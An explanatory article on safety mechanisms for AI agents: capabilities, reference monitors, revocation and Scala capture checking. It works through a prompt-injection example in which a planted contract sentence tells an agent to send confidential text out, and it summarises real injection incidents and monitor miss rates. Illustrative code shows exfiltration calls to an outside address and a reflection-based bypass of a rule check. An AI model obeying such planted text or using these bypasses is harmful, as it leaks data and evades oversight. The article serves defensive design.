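# Safety Layers in Programming Languages and Software Stacks for Advanced AI

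## What stands between an AI model's output and its effects

A safety layer in a programming language or operating system limits what a program can do, regardless of its author's intent. Examples include a compiler that rejects certain programs and the part of an operating system that blocks unauthorized users from opening a file. Engineers designed most of these layers for code written by people, and researchers are now adapting them to code and commands from AI models.

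Large language models, the systems behind products such as ChatGPT and Claude, produce text, which has no effect on its own. If a model writes "delete the file", the file remains unless other software deletes it. Developers turn a model into an *agent* by connecting it to software that lets it take actions, usually in a loop of acting and reading the results. The *scaffold* is the ordinary program code around the model that prompts it, runs its output and returns the results. A *tool call* is the model's request that the scaffold run a named function, such as reading a file or sending an email. An agent therefore affects the outside world only through software that somebody wrote and can change.

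Suppose a company wants an agent to read a folder of confidential contracts and write a summary into one file. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes a task of this kind, in which the agent must not leak the contracts and their wording must not steer it. Suppose also that the agent may use the network, because its model runs in a provider's cloud, and that one contract contains a planted instruction to send the full text to an address outside the company. The other party to the contract might have put it there in white type on a white page. The agent has good reason to hold each of its permissions, which are to read the contracts, write a file and use the network. The harm becomes possible because the agent can send what it reads over the network.

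### From text to effect

Suppose the model treats the planted sentence as an instruction. It then outputs a tool call containing the name of a sending function, the outside address and the contract text. Nothing is sent until the developer's application runs the call. *How tool use works*, Anthropic's guide for developers who build on Claude, states: "The model never runs anything on its own". The application extracts the function name and arguments from the model's reply, runs the operation and returns the result with the next request, repeating this as long as the replies contain tool calls. For a few tools, including web search, Anthropic runs the code on its own servers. Anthropic can stop those calls while they run, but the developer can mostly just choose whether to enable the tool.

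In the contracts case, the scaffold is the first layer that can stop the message. Its developer can leave out the sending function, check the address against a list, or hold the call until a person approves it. Human approval is an unreliable filter. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users of Claude Code, its programming agent, accept 93% of permission prompts, and describes a replacement in which a second model judges the riskier actions before they run. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (Willison, 2026) notes that Anthropic made auto mode the default for new sessions in most Claude Code plans from 14 August.

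Many agents write whole programs instead of issuing one tool call at a time, because a program can combine several tools and the logic between them in a single step. A *high-level language*, such as Python or Scala, lets the author of a program work with files, lists and messages without specifying processor instructions or memory addresses. A *compiler* translates the program into a lower-level form, and a *runtime* executes it and supplies services such as memory. An *object* bundles data with the functions that act on it. A file object, for example, holds the details of an open file and offers "read" and "write" functions. A *type* classifies an expression by the kind of value it yields, which determines what a program may do with it. For example, a program may multiply two numbers but not a number and a file. A *type system* is the set of rules a compiler uses to assign types and reject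 programs that combine expressions wrongly.

Both the compiler and the runtime can stop a model's output from taking effect. In TACIT, a system that Odersky and colleagues built, the agent submits snippets of Scala, and only those that pass the compiler's checks run. The runtime catches other violations. For example, if a program has permission for one folder and tries to access a path outside it, the attempt fails.

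To use the disk or the network card, a running program must still make a *system call*, a request to the operating system. The textbook chapter *Access Control Fundamentals* describes the mechanism that authorizes these requests by deciding whether a subject (a user or a running program) may perform an operation on a resource such as a file or a socket (one end of a network connection). To send the contract, the program must ask to open a socket to the outside address, and the operating system can refuse the request.

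The processor prevents the program from skipping the operating system. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) describes the simplest arrangement. Extra hardware checks every memory reference against a register that holds the lowest address the program may use and the count of locations beyond it. A reference outside that range fails. To stop ordinary programs from changing the register, the processor allows changes only while a "privileged" bit is on. Ordinary programs run with the bit off. The one instruction that lets them turn it on also hands control to the supervisor program, the ancestor of today's operating-system core, at an entry point planned in advance. The supervisor's tables lie outside the range that ordinary programs can reach, so the mechanism protects itself as well as the users. Processors today use far more elaborate versions of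 the same idea.

If the message gets past all of this, the network card sends the bytes. After that, only equipment further along the network, such as a company firewall, could still drop them.

Checks at lower layers of the stack have less information to act on. The scaffold receives a recipient and a readable document. The operating system receives a network address and a sequence of bytes, which may be encrypted, and the processor handles only instructions and memory references. A rule such as "No contract text leaves the company" is therefore easy to state near the top of the stack and almost impossible to express at the bottom. However, checks near the top are easier to bypass.

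### Authority, and where a program gets it

The *authority* of a piece of code is the set of effects it can cause. Saltzer and Schroeder recommended that every program run with the least privilege its job requires, mainly because this limits the damage from an accident or error. Common operating systems make this advice awkward to follow, because a program on Windows or Unix ordinarily runs with the rights of the user who started it. When the program requests an operation on a named file, the system checks the user's permissions. *Ambient authority* is authority that code has merely by running in a process or under an account, without anybody handing it over. If a lawyer starts the contracts agent from her own account, the agent can by default open her other clients' files and any passwords she has saved on the disk, even though nobody decided to give it that access.

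An *access control list* is attached to a resource and specifies which users or programs may do what with it. The contracts folder could have a list that lets a separate agent account read files but not change them. This is worth doing but does not solve the problem, because the agent must read the contracts to summarize them, and the list does not control where the text goes afterwards. The list also cannot distinguish a file that the agent opens for the lawyer from one that it opens because of the planted sentence. The main alternative is a *capability*, an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and gives the right to use it.

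A *sandbox* is a restricted environment that limits which system resources the code inside it can reach. The contracts agent could run in one that contains only the folder and the output file from the disk. Cutting off network access would make the planted instruction fail, but the agent would fail too because it needs the network to reach its cloud model. Anthropic describes sandboxing in general as safe, but says that someone has to configure each new function and that tools that need the network or the host machine break the isolation.

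One could let the sandbox connect only to the provider's address. The outside address would then be unreachable from inside, but someone would still have to decide whether the provider may receive contract text. Odersky and colleagues assume that it may not, and send confidential material to a separate, trusted model that runs locally. A company that has an agreement with its provider might decide differently. No layer can make this decision by itself, so somebody has to write a *policy*, a stated rule about which actions or data movements the company allows, before software can enforce it.

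### What a check needs in order to hold

Each guarantee in this field depends on a set of components that must work correctly, called the *trusted computing base*. For TACIT, Odersky and colleagues list the Scala compiler, their library, the runtime and, where a user has one, the local model for confidential text. In practice, the operating system and the processor belong there too, because the runtime depends on them. The cloud model that drives the agent, the agent's code and everything the agent reads are outside the base. A compiler bug could therefore void the guarantee, but the guarantee is designed to hold even if the cloud model cooperates fully with an attacker.

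The classic account of what a trustworthy check looks like came from the US Air Force, which wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, identified the hard case as a malicious user with legitimate access who can write and run arbitrary programs. That is a fair description of a hijacked agent that writes code. Barriers around the machine do not help when the attacker is already inside, so the defence has to sit in the process that controls program execution. Anderson's panel proposed a *reference monitor*, which checks each reference that a program makes to data, devices or other programs against a record of what the program's user may do. It set three requirements:

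- Nobody can tamper with the mechanism. Otherwise its verdicts mean nothing.
- The mechanism always operates. If some group of programs runs without the check, those programs become part of the security machinery and have to meet the same standard.
- The mechanism is small enough for complete analysis and testing. Without that, nobody can establish that it works correctly in all cases.

The panel applied the requirements to a computer of the day, the HIS 635 with its operating system GCOS III. The hardware kept each user's program inside its own memory, as required. But for input and output the program had to call the supervisor, and most of the supervisor ran with the memory check suspended, so the check did not always operate. If the supervisor is counted as part of the mechanism, then the mechanism contained 200,000 or 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse completely, and attackers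 in test exercises had already broken it several times. Anderson also doubted that such exercises could show a system was safe. The attackers had succeeded every time so far, but if a team had found no flaw, the system's security would still have been unknown. Similarly, an AI agent that has passed its safety tests may still have flaws that the tests did not find.

A scaffold that inspects tool calls falls short of this standard if one of the tools is a shell, a program that runs whatever command it receives. The scaffold checks the request to start the command, but it can't check what the command, or any script it launches, then does. Anthropic encountered this problem with standing permissions that users had set up for convenience, some of which covered all shell commands or any Python script. Its automatic mode drops such rules when it starts, because they would let the commands most able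 to do damage skip review. Anthropic concedes that its list of rules to drop will always be incomplete. An operating system comes closer to checking everything, but it is much larger than Anderson's third requirement calls for.

### Error, injection and aims of its own

An agent may send the contracts to the wrong place by mistake. Anthropic keeps an internal log of incidents in which Claude misread an instruction and deleted remote branches of a code repository, uploaded an engineer's access token to an internal computing cluster, and tried to change the structure of a live database. Anthropic separates honest mistakes, such as assuming a shared resource is a test copy, from overeagerness, where the agent understands the goal but goes further than the user would approve. When one user asked an agent to "cancel my job", the agent tried to delete the job with the most similar name. Honest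 mistakes and overeagerness both count as errors for a check outside the model.

*Prompt injection* is different because someone intends the harm. It is text planted in data the agent reads that the model takes as an instruction, like the sentence in the contract. It is named after SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types database commands into a field such as a web form. Programmers can prevent SQL injection by passing commands and data to the database separately, but a language model has no such separation. ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning over growing AI prompt injection risks* quotes an official of Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), who explains that a model only predicts the next token (a word or part of a word) from all the text so far, so complete protection may never be possible. NCSC's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* advises designers to assume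 that, in the worst case, an attacker could do anything that direct access to the agent's tools would allow.

This has happened to widely used products, though in the cases below researchers found the flaws and the companies have since fixed them. Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data* describes how instructions in an email could make ChatGPT pass private data to an attacker. OpenAI had already blocked an earlier version of the attack by forbidding ChatGPT to alter web links, but the new version used unaltered links. The Hacker News' *Google Gemini Prompt Injection Flaw Exposed Private Calendar Data via Malicious Invites* (2026) covers a case even closer to the contracts. Using only ordinary calendar operations, text in an invitation led Google's Gemini to summarize the user's private meetings and write the summary into a new event, which in many companies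 the attacker could read. Criminals are now developing their own tools for such attacks, according to Underhill's *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026).

The remaining possibility is that the model pursues goals its developers did not intend, which researchers call misalignment. The agent might then send the contracts out without any planted sentence, because doing so serves a goal it acquired in training.

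A check outside the model can work without identifying why the model made a call. It compares the message's address and data with the policy, and the result is the same whether the call came from a mistake, text written by a stranger or the model's own goal. Anthropic reaches this conclusion about its own categories, saying that the defence in every case is to block the action. This matters because the cause is often hard to establish even after the message is sent, and harder still beforehand.

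How strong a check must be depends on whether it guards against mistakes or deliberate attacks. A careless agent hits a gap in the rules only by chance, whereas an attacker or a hostile model can search for one. Many commercial systems in 1975 had features that caught users' mistakes, but Saltzer and Schroeder warned against calling that security. A layer meant to work whatever the cause must assume a deliberate attack. Odersky and colleagues make this assumption, and add that when hundreds or thousands of agents work largely unsupervised, simple mistakes alone are very likely to open serious holes.

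### Rules around the model and rules inside it

A developer can also try to prevent the leak by training the model to ignore instructions in documents, or by writing "never disclose contract text" into its prompt. An engineer can read a line of scaffold code that compares an address with a list, work out what it does for every possible address, and correct it. Rules given to the model can't be checked and corrected in this way, because the model's behaviour lies in its *weights*, the numbers that training adjusts, and the rule about contracts isn't written out anywhere in them. A written prompt is readable, but it takes effect only through the weights. SecurityBrief UK, in its account of the NCSC's guidance, makes the same distinction between patterns from training data and strict enforcement of rules.

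Rules inside the model help, though how much depends on the model. Odersky and colleagues asked two agents for secrets, outright or under false pretences, in 11 different ways, with no protection beyond the models' own training. Claude Sonnet 4.6 revealed secrets in two cases and MiniMax M2.5 in eight. The sample is small, but the gap is wide. More training does not reliably fix this. Zorz (2026) reports in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* that training on more injection attacks left agents easier to hijack, and that a large collection of attacks may contain the same one many times.

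Some rules fall between the two kinds. The second model in Claude Code's automatic mode runs outside the agent, and ordinary code enforces its verdict, but the verdict comes from learned weights. By Anthropic's count, it let through 17% of 52 real cases of overeager behaviour. Because the weights are learned, nobody can fix these misses by finding and correcting a faulty line of code. The NCSC advises designing for the failures that will remain. Infosecurity Magazine's *UK NCSC Raises Alarms Over Prompt Injection Attacks* quotes its warning that a language model may be the wrong tool for a system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk.

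Readable rules around the model have a different weakness, which is that they can miss harm done through permitted actions. If the planted sentence had been an instruction to leave a penalty clause out of the summary, the agent would have read a permitted folder and written to a permitted file, and no rule about files or addresses would have stopped it.

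## Objects as permissions in object-oriented code

An obvious way to enforce a rule on agent-written code is to build the check into something all that code must use. In object-oriented languages such as Java and Python, a *class* is a template for objects, and a new class can extend an existing *base class* and inherit its functions, known as *methods*. A developer could write a base class whose `act()` method compares every action with the company's rule, and require all agent code to extend it. Marking the method *final* stops the agent's class from replacing it. For the contracts agent, the result might look like this:

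```
class SafeAgent:
    private rule
    final method act(action):
        if rule.allows(action): perform(action)
        else: refuse(action)

class ContractsAgent extends SafeAgent:
    method summarize():
        text = files.read("contracts/acme")
        network.send(outside_address, text)
```

The last two lines never call `act()`. `files` and `network` are libraries that come with the language, and any code in the program can use them, whatever class it extends. The contract therefore leaves the company even if the rule is perfect and the method cannot be changed. In Anderson's terms, the mechanism does not always operate.

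Suppose the developer now rejects any agent code that calls those libraries directly. Many languages also offer *reflection*, a set of features that let a running program inspect and alter its own parts:

```
        reflection.set(this, "rule", allow_everything)
        act(send(outside_address, text))
```

This time the check runs and approves the message, because the agent's code has replaced the rule.

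*Joe-E* (Mettler, Wagner and Close, 2010) illustrates the problem with a tiny Java class that keeps a log. The log's text sits in a private field, and the only method for changing it adds an entry. In ordinary Java, other code can still alter old entries, even though the class appears to prevent this. Reflection can ignore the "private" label. *Native methods*, which run code from outside Java, can do anything. The standard library also lets all code write to any file that the Java runtime can reach, including the one where the log is stored. A reviewer has to read the whole application to be sure that nothing uses these routes, and the review would never end if an agent kept writing new programs.

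Developers can start the agent's code with no routes and give it only the few it needs. Blocking the routes one by one is unpromising because a standard library contains so many.

### The object-capability model

*Thinking About Capabilities* (Shapiro, 2004) traces the term "capability" to a 1966 paper on operating systems by Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn. The doctoral thesis *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006) presents their model in a form that also fits programming languages, where it needs few new mechanisms. Objects in a running program already hold references to one another, and an object uses another by sending it a message, which in most languages means calling a method. If objects can interact only in this way, holding a reference to an object gives permission to use it.

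In this model, *devices* are objects connected to things like a disk or a network. Code can affect the outside world only by sending a message to a device, directly or through other objects. But withholding a reference does not protect plain data, such as a number or a password, because anyone who can work it out has it.

Everything then depends on how an object comes to hold a reference. Miller allows four ways:

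- **Initial conditions:** the object already held the reference when the system started.
- **Parenthood:** an object that creates another receives the only reference to it.
- **Endowment:** the creator can give the new object references that the creator already holds.
- **Introduction:** an object that holds references to two others can send one of them a message containing a reference to the other.

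When objects serve as permissions, code can reach a resource only through a chain of references, so knowing a file's name or running under the right user account does not give it access. Miller summarizes this as "only connectivity begets connectivity". If the agent's code has no chain of references to the network, it cannot make one itself. An object that can already reach both the agent and the network would have to introduce them. A reviewer can therefore concentrate on the few objects that connect the agent to everything else.

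Somebody must still decide which objects a program starts with. *Objects as Secure Capabilities* (Duffy, 2015) describes a whole system that worked this way. Each program came with a manifest of what it needed, the system decided whether to grant the request, and the program's main function received the resulting objects. This keeps the policy decision in one visible place.

### What the language has to rule out

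An object-capability program needs its language to make certain operations impossible. The language must have *memory safety*, so that code can't read or write memory except through valid references. C++ fails this requirement because a program can turn an integer into a pointer and so forge a reference. The language must also prevent objects from accessing each other's private state, which rules out the reflection trick. It must forbid global variables that hold changeable objects, because any code could get a reference from them without an introduction. Libraries must not give code authority merely because it knows their names, since that would bring back ambient authority.

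Agents write new programs while the system is running, which makes one further condition important. The *loader*, which turns program text into a running object, must give that object only the references that the loader's caller supplies. Miller calls this loader isolation. Java lacks it because some system names that carry authority are always available to loaded code, even though the caller can decide what most names refer to.

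Miller and his collaborators built the language E around the model. E's loader still recognizes a few names that the caller did not supply, which Miller admits violates the model, though mostly harmlessly. Joe-E instead removes the parts of Java that violate the model. Its checker keeps mutable objects out of global variables, and programs can use only a safe portion of the standard library.

Mettler and colleagues illustrate the benefit with an image viewer that loads decoders written by strangers. Each decoder receives bytes, returns a picture, and holds no other references. Joe-E's checker uses Java's type system to confirm that a decoder cannot store anything between calls, so the worst a malicious one can do is return the wrong picture. Some newer languages, including the Scala used in TACIT, go further and record capabilities in the types themselves.

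### The contracts agent with two kinds of object

In an object-capability language, the company's own launcher program could start the contracts agent like this:

```
class ReadOnlyDocument:
    private file
    method read(): return file.read()

class SummaryFile:
    private file
    method write(text): file.write(text)

documents = a ReadOnlyDocument for each file in contracts_folder
summary   = SummaryFile(disk.create("summary"))
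load(agent_code, documents, summary)
```

The agent's code receives the documents and the summary file by endowment, and nothing else. It can't alter a contract, because `ReadOnlyDocument` has no method for that and keeps the real file object private. Programmers call this *attenuation*, which means handing over an object that allows less than the one behind it. If the model follows the planted sentence and writes `network.send(...)`, the call fails because the name `network` refers to nothing, so the programmer doesn't need to write a list of forbidden addresses.

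The scaffold still holds a network reference, so if it sends the result of `read()` to the cloud model, the provider receives the contract text.

Miller also distinguishes *permission*, which is a direct reference, from *authority*, which includes everything that code can cause indirectly. Suppose another program publishes the summary file on a website every night. The agent's code then has the authority to publish the contracts by copying them into the summary, even though it has no permission to use the network.

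Working out exactly what a piece of code will ever be able to cause is intractable, because the answer depends on the behaviour of every program involved. Miller instead uses larger sets that certainly contain the answer:

actual authority ⊆ bound from references and known behaviour ⊆ bound from references alone

The outermost set is easy to compute by following references and assuming that every object is hostile, but it is too pessimistic. It includes the possibility that `ReadOnlyDocument` exposes its private file, which a quick look at its code rules out. Reading the trusted objects' code gives the tighter, middle bound. This approach suits agents rather well because the company can inspect a few lines of its own code and treat everything the model writes as hostile.

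### Taking access back

A plain reference works for as long as its holder keeps it. If the launcher wants to end the agent's access when the summary is ready, it has to plan for this in advance. David Redell described the standard technique, the *caretaker*, in 1974. In simplified form:

```
function make_revocable(target):
    enabled = true
    forwarder = object that, on any message:
        if enabled: pass it to target and return the reply
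        else: fail
    switch = object with method off(): enabled = false
    return forwarder, switch
```

The launcher gives the agent the forwarder and keeps the switch. If the agent has shared the forwarder with helper programs, calling `off()` also ends their access, because they never had a reference to the document itself.

The caretaker doesn't control references contained in the target's replies. If the target is a folder that returns file objects, the agent holds those files directly and can keep using them after the launcher turns off the folder. Miller's thesis solves this with a *membrane*, which wraps every reference that crosses it, in either direction, in another forwarder, and one switch controls all the forwarders. The membrane leaves plain data unwrapped, because revocation can stop the agent from opening a contract again but can't take back text the agent has already read.

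### The confused deputy

In *Capability Myths Demolished*, Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003) retell a story that Norm Hardy published in 1988. A compiler on a shared computer had permission to write to a file called BILL, where it recorded what users owed. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. When a user typed "BILL", the compiler overwrote the billing records. The user had no permission to write to that file, but the system checked only the compiler's permissions.

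A *deputy* is a program that manages authority from more than one source, and it becomes *confused* when someone manipulates it into using that authority for the wrong purpose. In this case, the user supplied the name and the compiler the permission. With capabilities, the user would have to pass a reference to the debugging file instead of a name. She can't pass a reference to BILL because she doesn't have one.

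Prompt injection makes an agent especially prone to the confused deputy problem. If the agent's tools accept names, the planted sentence can name an outside address or another client's file. If the tools require object references instead, text cannot supply one, but it can still lead the agent to misuse references it legitimately holds, as with the omitted penalty clause. The problem also returns in full if a developer adds, for convenience, a function that opens any file by name.

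Miller and colleagues note that removing ambient authority makes it possible to write a deputy that nobody can confuse, but the programmer still has to keep track of what each reference is for. A program that tries every reference it holds until one works is no safer than one with ambient authority.

### Access control lists or capabilities

A common comparison of access control lists and capabilities uses a table with a row for each user or program and a column for each resource. Each cell contains the rights of that user or program over that resource. An access control list stores a column with its resource, while a capability system stores a row with its user or program. In this comparison, the two approaches appear to differ only in where they store the rights.

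Miller and colleagues call this a myth, because the table records rights at a single moment and leaves out the rules for changing them. An access control list must name the users or programs it covers, so administrators prefer names that rarely change, such as user accounts. When Miller and colleagues wrote, they knew of no system based on these lists that treated each running process as a separate party. In a capability system, every object can have its own rights. If an agent starts twenty helpers for a few minutes and each needs one document, the agent can pass each helper one reference, which is much simpler than creating twenty accounts and editing the lists.

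An older objection was that capabilities spread out of control. W. E. Boebert argued in 1984 that a program with low security clearance could write one of its capabilities into memory that a high-clearance program could read, and the high-clearance program could then use it to leak secrets to low-clearance programs. The attack works only if capabilities can be read and written as ordinary data. Most capability systems keep the two separate, so permission to read data does not let a program obtain a capability.

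Language models mostly read and write text. If a permission is a secret string, as with some tokens that a gateway checks, a model that sees the string could copy it into a summary, which it cannot do with an object reference.

Gutmann (2015), in a mailing-list reply, compared the paper to an imaginary "Monorail Myths Demolished", complaining that one can demolish any myth by choosing examples carefully and offering solutions that need not work in practice. This is closer to a jibe than an argument, but there are real practical difficulties.

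Programmers have to pass references explicitly. If a function deep inside a program writes the summary, every function on the way to it may have to accept the reference and pass it on. A library that used to open its own settings file now needs its caller to supply the file. Mettler and colleagues concede that most existing Java code is not valid Joe-E, and that the valid code is often not structured to benefit from the language. They designed it for new programs. Agents write a lot of new code, which weakens the objection, but that code usually depends on old libraries. In a program that mixes the two languages, all the ordinary Java stays in the trusted computing base.

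Revocation is possible, as the caretaker shows, but it has to be planned in advance. A launcher that has handed out the bare file object can't recall it, whereas an administrator can edit an access control list at any time.

Auditing remains difficult. With an access control list, a security officer can immediately look up who can read a particular contract. Paul Karger and Andrew Herbert proposed a similar list for capability systems in 1984, but Miller points out that it would omit anyone who holds only a forwarder. Programmers who follow good practice and attenuate access would therefore make the list useless. Miller adds that access control lists have the same gap, since a Unix process can read a file and pass the contents to others. That is true, but the officer of a capability system still has to trace the references and read the forwarders' code to find out who can read the contract.

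### Hardened JavaScript

Object capabilities have reached everyday software through JavaScript, the main programming language of web pages. Ordinary JavaScript does not fully follow the object-capability model because any code can alter built-in objects that the whole program shares. Conffab's recorded talk *Hardened JavaScript* describes how the built-in function constructor also violates the model by turning text into a program that can reach the global variables.

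The project's page, *Hardened JavaScript*, describes three tools that close these holes. `lockdown()` freezes the shared built-in objects and stops code from reaching the true global variables through the function constructor. `harden()` freezes an object and everything reachable through its properties, so one recipient can't replace its methods to spy on another. A `Compartment` runs code with its own global variables, to which the host adds only the powerful objects it chooses. For the contracts agent, these would be the documents and the summary file.

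LavaMoat, a set of security tools for JavaScript projects, uses Hardened JavaScript to limit the damage from tampered third-party libraries. Its glossary uses the older name, Secure ECMAScript or SES, and describes it as a proposal on the way to standardization. MetaMask, a cryptocurrency wallet, uses LavaMoat in its browser extension and also confines plugins with Hardened JavaScript. Endo, a platform under development, extends the approach to objects on machines that do not trust each other. Its developers report that most libraries for Node.js, a common JavaScript runtime, can be used unmodified because they rarely change global variables or built-in objects. This is much better compatibility than Joe-E offers, although a library that needs a file or a connection must still get it from other code.

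Compartments do not prevent code from entering an infinite loop and halting everything else in the same process. They have no clock by default, because code with a clock can infer secrets from how long operations take. Many programs need a clock, and the project advises hosts that supply one to keep confidential information out of that process.

### Revocable permissions for coding agents

*Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, June 2026) applies revocation to agents that edit software. Such agents often keep a permission for a whole task when they need it for only one step. The paper's system, PORTICO, is a reference monitor between the model and its tools, so it does not require a special programming language. It gives the model *handles*, opaque references that each permit particular operations on a particular resource.

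A person first writes a task specification that lists the files available from the start, the files the agent may request later, the events that end each grant, and whatever is off limits. In the paper's main example, an agent has to add a timeout setting to one file and carry it through to a second. It starts with handles for the first file and its test. When it asks for the second file, the monitor finds a matching rule and issues new handles for the next step. Once the tests pass, the monitor removes those handles and rejects any attempt to reuse them. The model cannot extend a grant by claiming it still needs the file, because the monitor relies on trusted events, such as the result of a test it launched itself or approval from an authenticated person.

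Santos-Grueiro tested the design mainly with Qwen3-Coder 30B, an open model. Seventeen scenarios placed forbidden resources within the agent's reach. In a second set of 37 tasks, many required files outside the initial scope. He ran each scenario and task five times.

| Setup | Runs with a forbidden effect (17 scenarios) | Tasks completed (37 tasks) |
|---|---|---|
| Full access | 100% | 97% |
| Fixed list of allowed tools and paths | 82% | 97% |
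| Coarse sandbox | 86% | 97% |
| PORTICO, initial permissions only | 0% | 21% |
| PORTICO with temporary grants | 0% | 87% |

The zero violation counts are less meaningful than the completion figures, because PORTICO enforced rules from the same specification that was used to score violations. Fixed minimal permissions made the agent nearly useless on these tasks, and temporary grants recovered most of the loss.

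To isolate the effect of revocation, Santos-Grueiro built a version of PORTICO that issued the same grants at the same moments but never withdrew them. Both versions completed all ten runs of one test. Afterwards, the version without revocation let the agent reread the temporary file in all ten runs, while PORTICO refused each time. In six cases, a live model tried to reuse an old permission to change a file, alter version-control data or contact a network host. Every attempt succeeded without revocation, and none succeeded with it. These results confirm that the mechanism works as designed, but they do not measure how often real agents would misuse an old permission.

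Evidence from real software is weaker. On 14 tasks drawn from eight Python projects, every setup, including full access, finished every task without a violation, so PORTICO had no harm to prevent. In 42 supplementary runs, PORTICO completed 31, while the version without revocation completed all 42. Some specifications ended a grant too early or offered no way to renew it, and sometimes the model failed to request access again. Santos-Grueiro did not measure the work of writing the specifications.

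The guarantee also covers only calls that pass through the monitor. PORTICO either refuses shell commands it cannot classify or holds them for explicit approval.

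## Type systems that reject unsafe agent code before it runs

PORTICO checks each tool call as it arrives, so when it rejects one, the earlier calls have already taken effect. A compiler can check a whole program before any of it runs. This is useful for agents that act by writing programs, if a program's type shows what the program might do.

In most languages, a function's type doesn't show everything the function does. A Java function that counts the words in a contract can have the same type as one that also emails the contract to a stranger, because both take text and return a number. Sending the email is an *effect*, which is anything a computation does besides returning a value. A *pure function*, such as one that only counts the words, has no effects. Some type systems record effects and give the two word counters different types. The compiler can then reject any agent program whose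 type includes a forbidden effect.

A program rejected before it runs can't leave a task half done. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that has to subtract 50 from a balance and return the new figure. The model writes one line that subtracts the 50 and another that returns a sentence where the caller expects a number. The Scala compiler rejects both lines together, so the balance stays the same. In a language that finds such errors only at run time, the program would subtract the 50 before it reached the faulty line.

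Even with object references, the scaffold could still pass the contract text to the cloud model. Types can also prevent this, by letting a program work on the text while stopping the text, and anything computed from it, from getting out.

### Capture sets and sealed data in TACIT

TACIT connects to existing agents through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for giving models access to tools. The agent must be able to act only by submitting Scala code, because shell access would let it bypass the compiler. *Safe Scala an introduction*, from the Scala consultancy VirtusLab, recommends turning all the agent's other tools into library functions that its Scala code can call.

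TACIT relies on *capture checking*, an experimental feature of Scala 3 that adds to a value's type a list of the capabilities the value can reach. This list is the *capture set*. Suppose `out` is a capability for writing to a file. A function that takes text and returns nothing useful (`Unit` in Scala) could have any of these types:

| Type | What the function may use |
|---|---|
| `String -> Unit` | no capabilities, so it is pure |
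| `String ->{out} Unit` | only `out` |
| `String => Unit` | any capability |

The compiler infers the set of capabilities a function may use from the function's code. The set is an upper bound, so a function that writes to `out` only under some conditions still has `out` in its type. The compiler accepts a function only if its set contains nothing beyond what the program allows at that point. Wrapping a capability in another object does not hide it. A logger that holds `out` has the type `Logger^{out}`, and the type of any function that uses the logger also accounts for `out`. An auditor can therefore see the limit of what a function can reach from its type, without reading its code.

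Odersky and colleagues use this to seal confidential data inside a wrapper:

```
class Classified[T]:
    def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`T` and `U` stand for any types, so a `Classified[String]` is a sealed piece of text. The agent's code cannot take the text out, but it can pass a function to `map`, which applies the function to the text and seals the result. The thin arrow in `T -> U` protects the text by restricting `map` to pure functions.

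With TACIT's library, the contracts agent could submit this program, which the compiler accepts:

```
requestFileSystem("/contracts") {
    val contract = readClassified("/contracts/acme.txt")
    val prompt   = contract.map(text => "Summarize: " + text)
    val summary  = chat(prompt)
    writeClassified("/contracts/summary.txt", summary)
}
```

The function passed to `map` only joins two pieces of text. `chat` sends the sealed prompt to the trusted local model and returns a sealed answer. The cloud model wrote the program but never receives the contract, so the planted sentence can't influence it.

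Now suppose the cloud model is itself hostile and the company has allowed the agent to use the network:

```
requestFileSystem("/contracts") {
    val contract = readClassified("/contracts/acme.txt")
    requestNetwork(allowedHosts) {
        contract.map(text => httpPost(outsideAddress, text))
    }
}
```

The function passed to `map` now uses the network, so its capture set is not empty and the compiler rejects the program. The compiler would reject it even if the outside address were on the list of allowed hosts, because the decision does not depend on the address. In tests by Odersky and colleagues, real agents wrote similar code. One tried to print a GitHub key from inside `map`, and another tried to write classified recommendations to a file. The compiler rejected both programs and identified the capability that each function should not have used.

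The user still needs to read the summary, so when a program prints a sealed value, TACIT sends the content to the user's terminal and only the text `Classified(****)` to the agent. If the user then asks how long the summary is, the agent can write `summary.map(_.length)` and print the result, which again only the user can see. The protection therefore lasts through a conversation, but the agent can't read the summary to check whether it makes sense.

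### Permissions that end with their block

In the programs above, `requestFileSystem` creates a capability for one folder, and the code between the braces can use it. The capability expires when the block ends. An agent might try to keep it by returning a function that opens a file later:

```
val later = requestFileSystem("/contracts") { fs =>
    () => fs.access("/contracts/acme.txt").read()
}
```

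The returned function's type would have to include `fs` in its capture set, but `fs` has no meaning outside the block, so the compiler rejects the program. The same rule covers the file objects that `fs` returns, because their types also include `fs`. The simple caretaker, by contrast, loses control of any file object that a folder has returned. In the tests, one agent tried to return a list of such files from the block, probably without bad intent, and the compiler rejected the code.

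`requestFileSystem` itself requires a general input/output capability. Code inside `map` has no capabilities, so it can't open a new block to get the data out. Permissions to run commands and use the network work the same way, with a list of command names or hosts in place of the folder. The compiler can't determine which paths a program will compute, so the library checks each path against the folder at run time.

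Scala can also pass capabilities implicitly, which spares programmers much of the work of passing them from function to function. It can even allow global capabilities, which the object-capability model forbids, because a function's type shows which ones it uses.

### Safe mode and the trusted parts

Ordinary Scala has features that would defeat all this. A *type cast*, for example, tells the compiler to treat a value as having a different type. An agent could use one to relabel a function that uses the network as a pure function. TACIT therefore compiles agent code in *safe mode*, which imposes six restrictions:

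1. The code may not use unchecked type casts or unchecked pattern matches.
2. It may not use the `caps.unsafe` module, which contains exemptions from capture checking.
3. It may not use `@unchecked` annotations, which switch off compiler checks.
4. It may not use reflection at run time.
5. It must compile with capture checking, including the tracking of all changes to stored data, and with explicit tracking of null (missing) values.
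6. It may use global objects and functions only if their own implementation is safe.

Someone still has to write the code that accesses the disk and the network. Scala's official *Safe Mode* documentation describes an `@assumeSafe` annotation for library modules that a programmer has verified by other means. Its example is a mailer that shows the user each email and sends it only if they agree. Agents can call this mailer but not the unrestricted one behind it, and they can't put the annotation on their own code. However, the compiler doesn't check that annotated modules are safe, so one careless `@assumeSafe` can create a security hole for every agent that uses the library.

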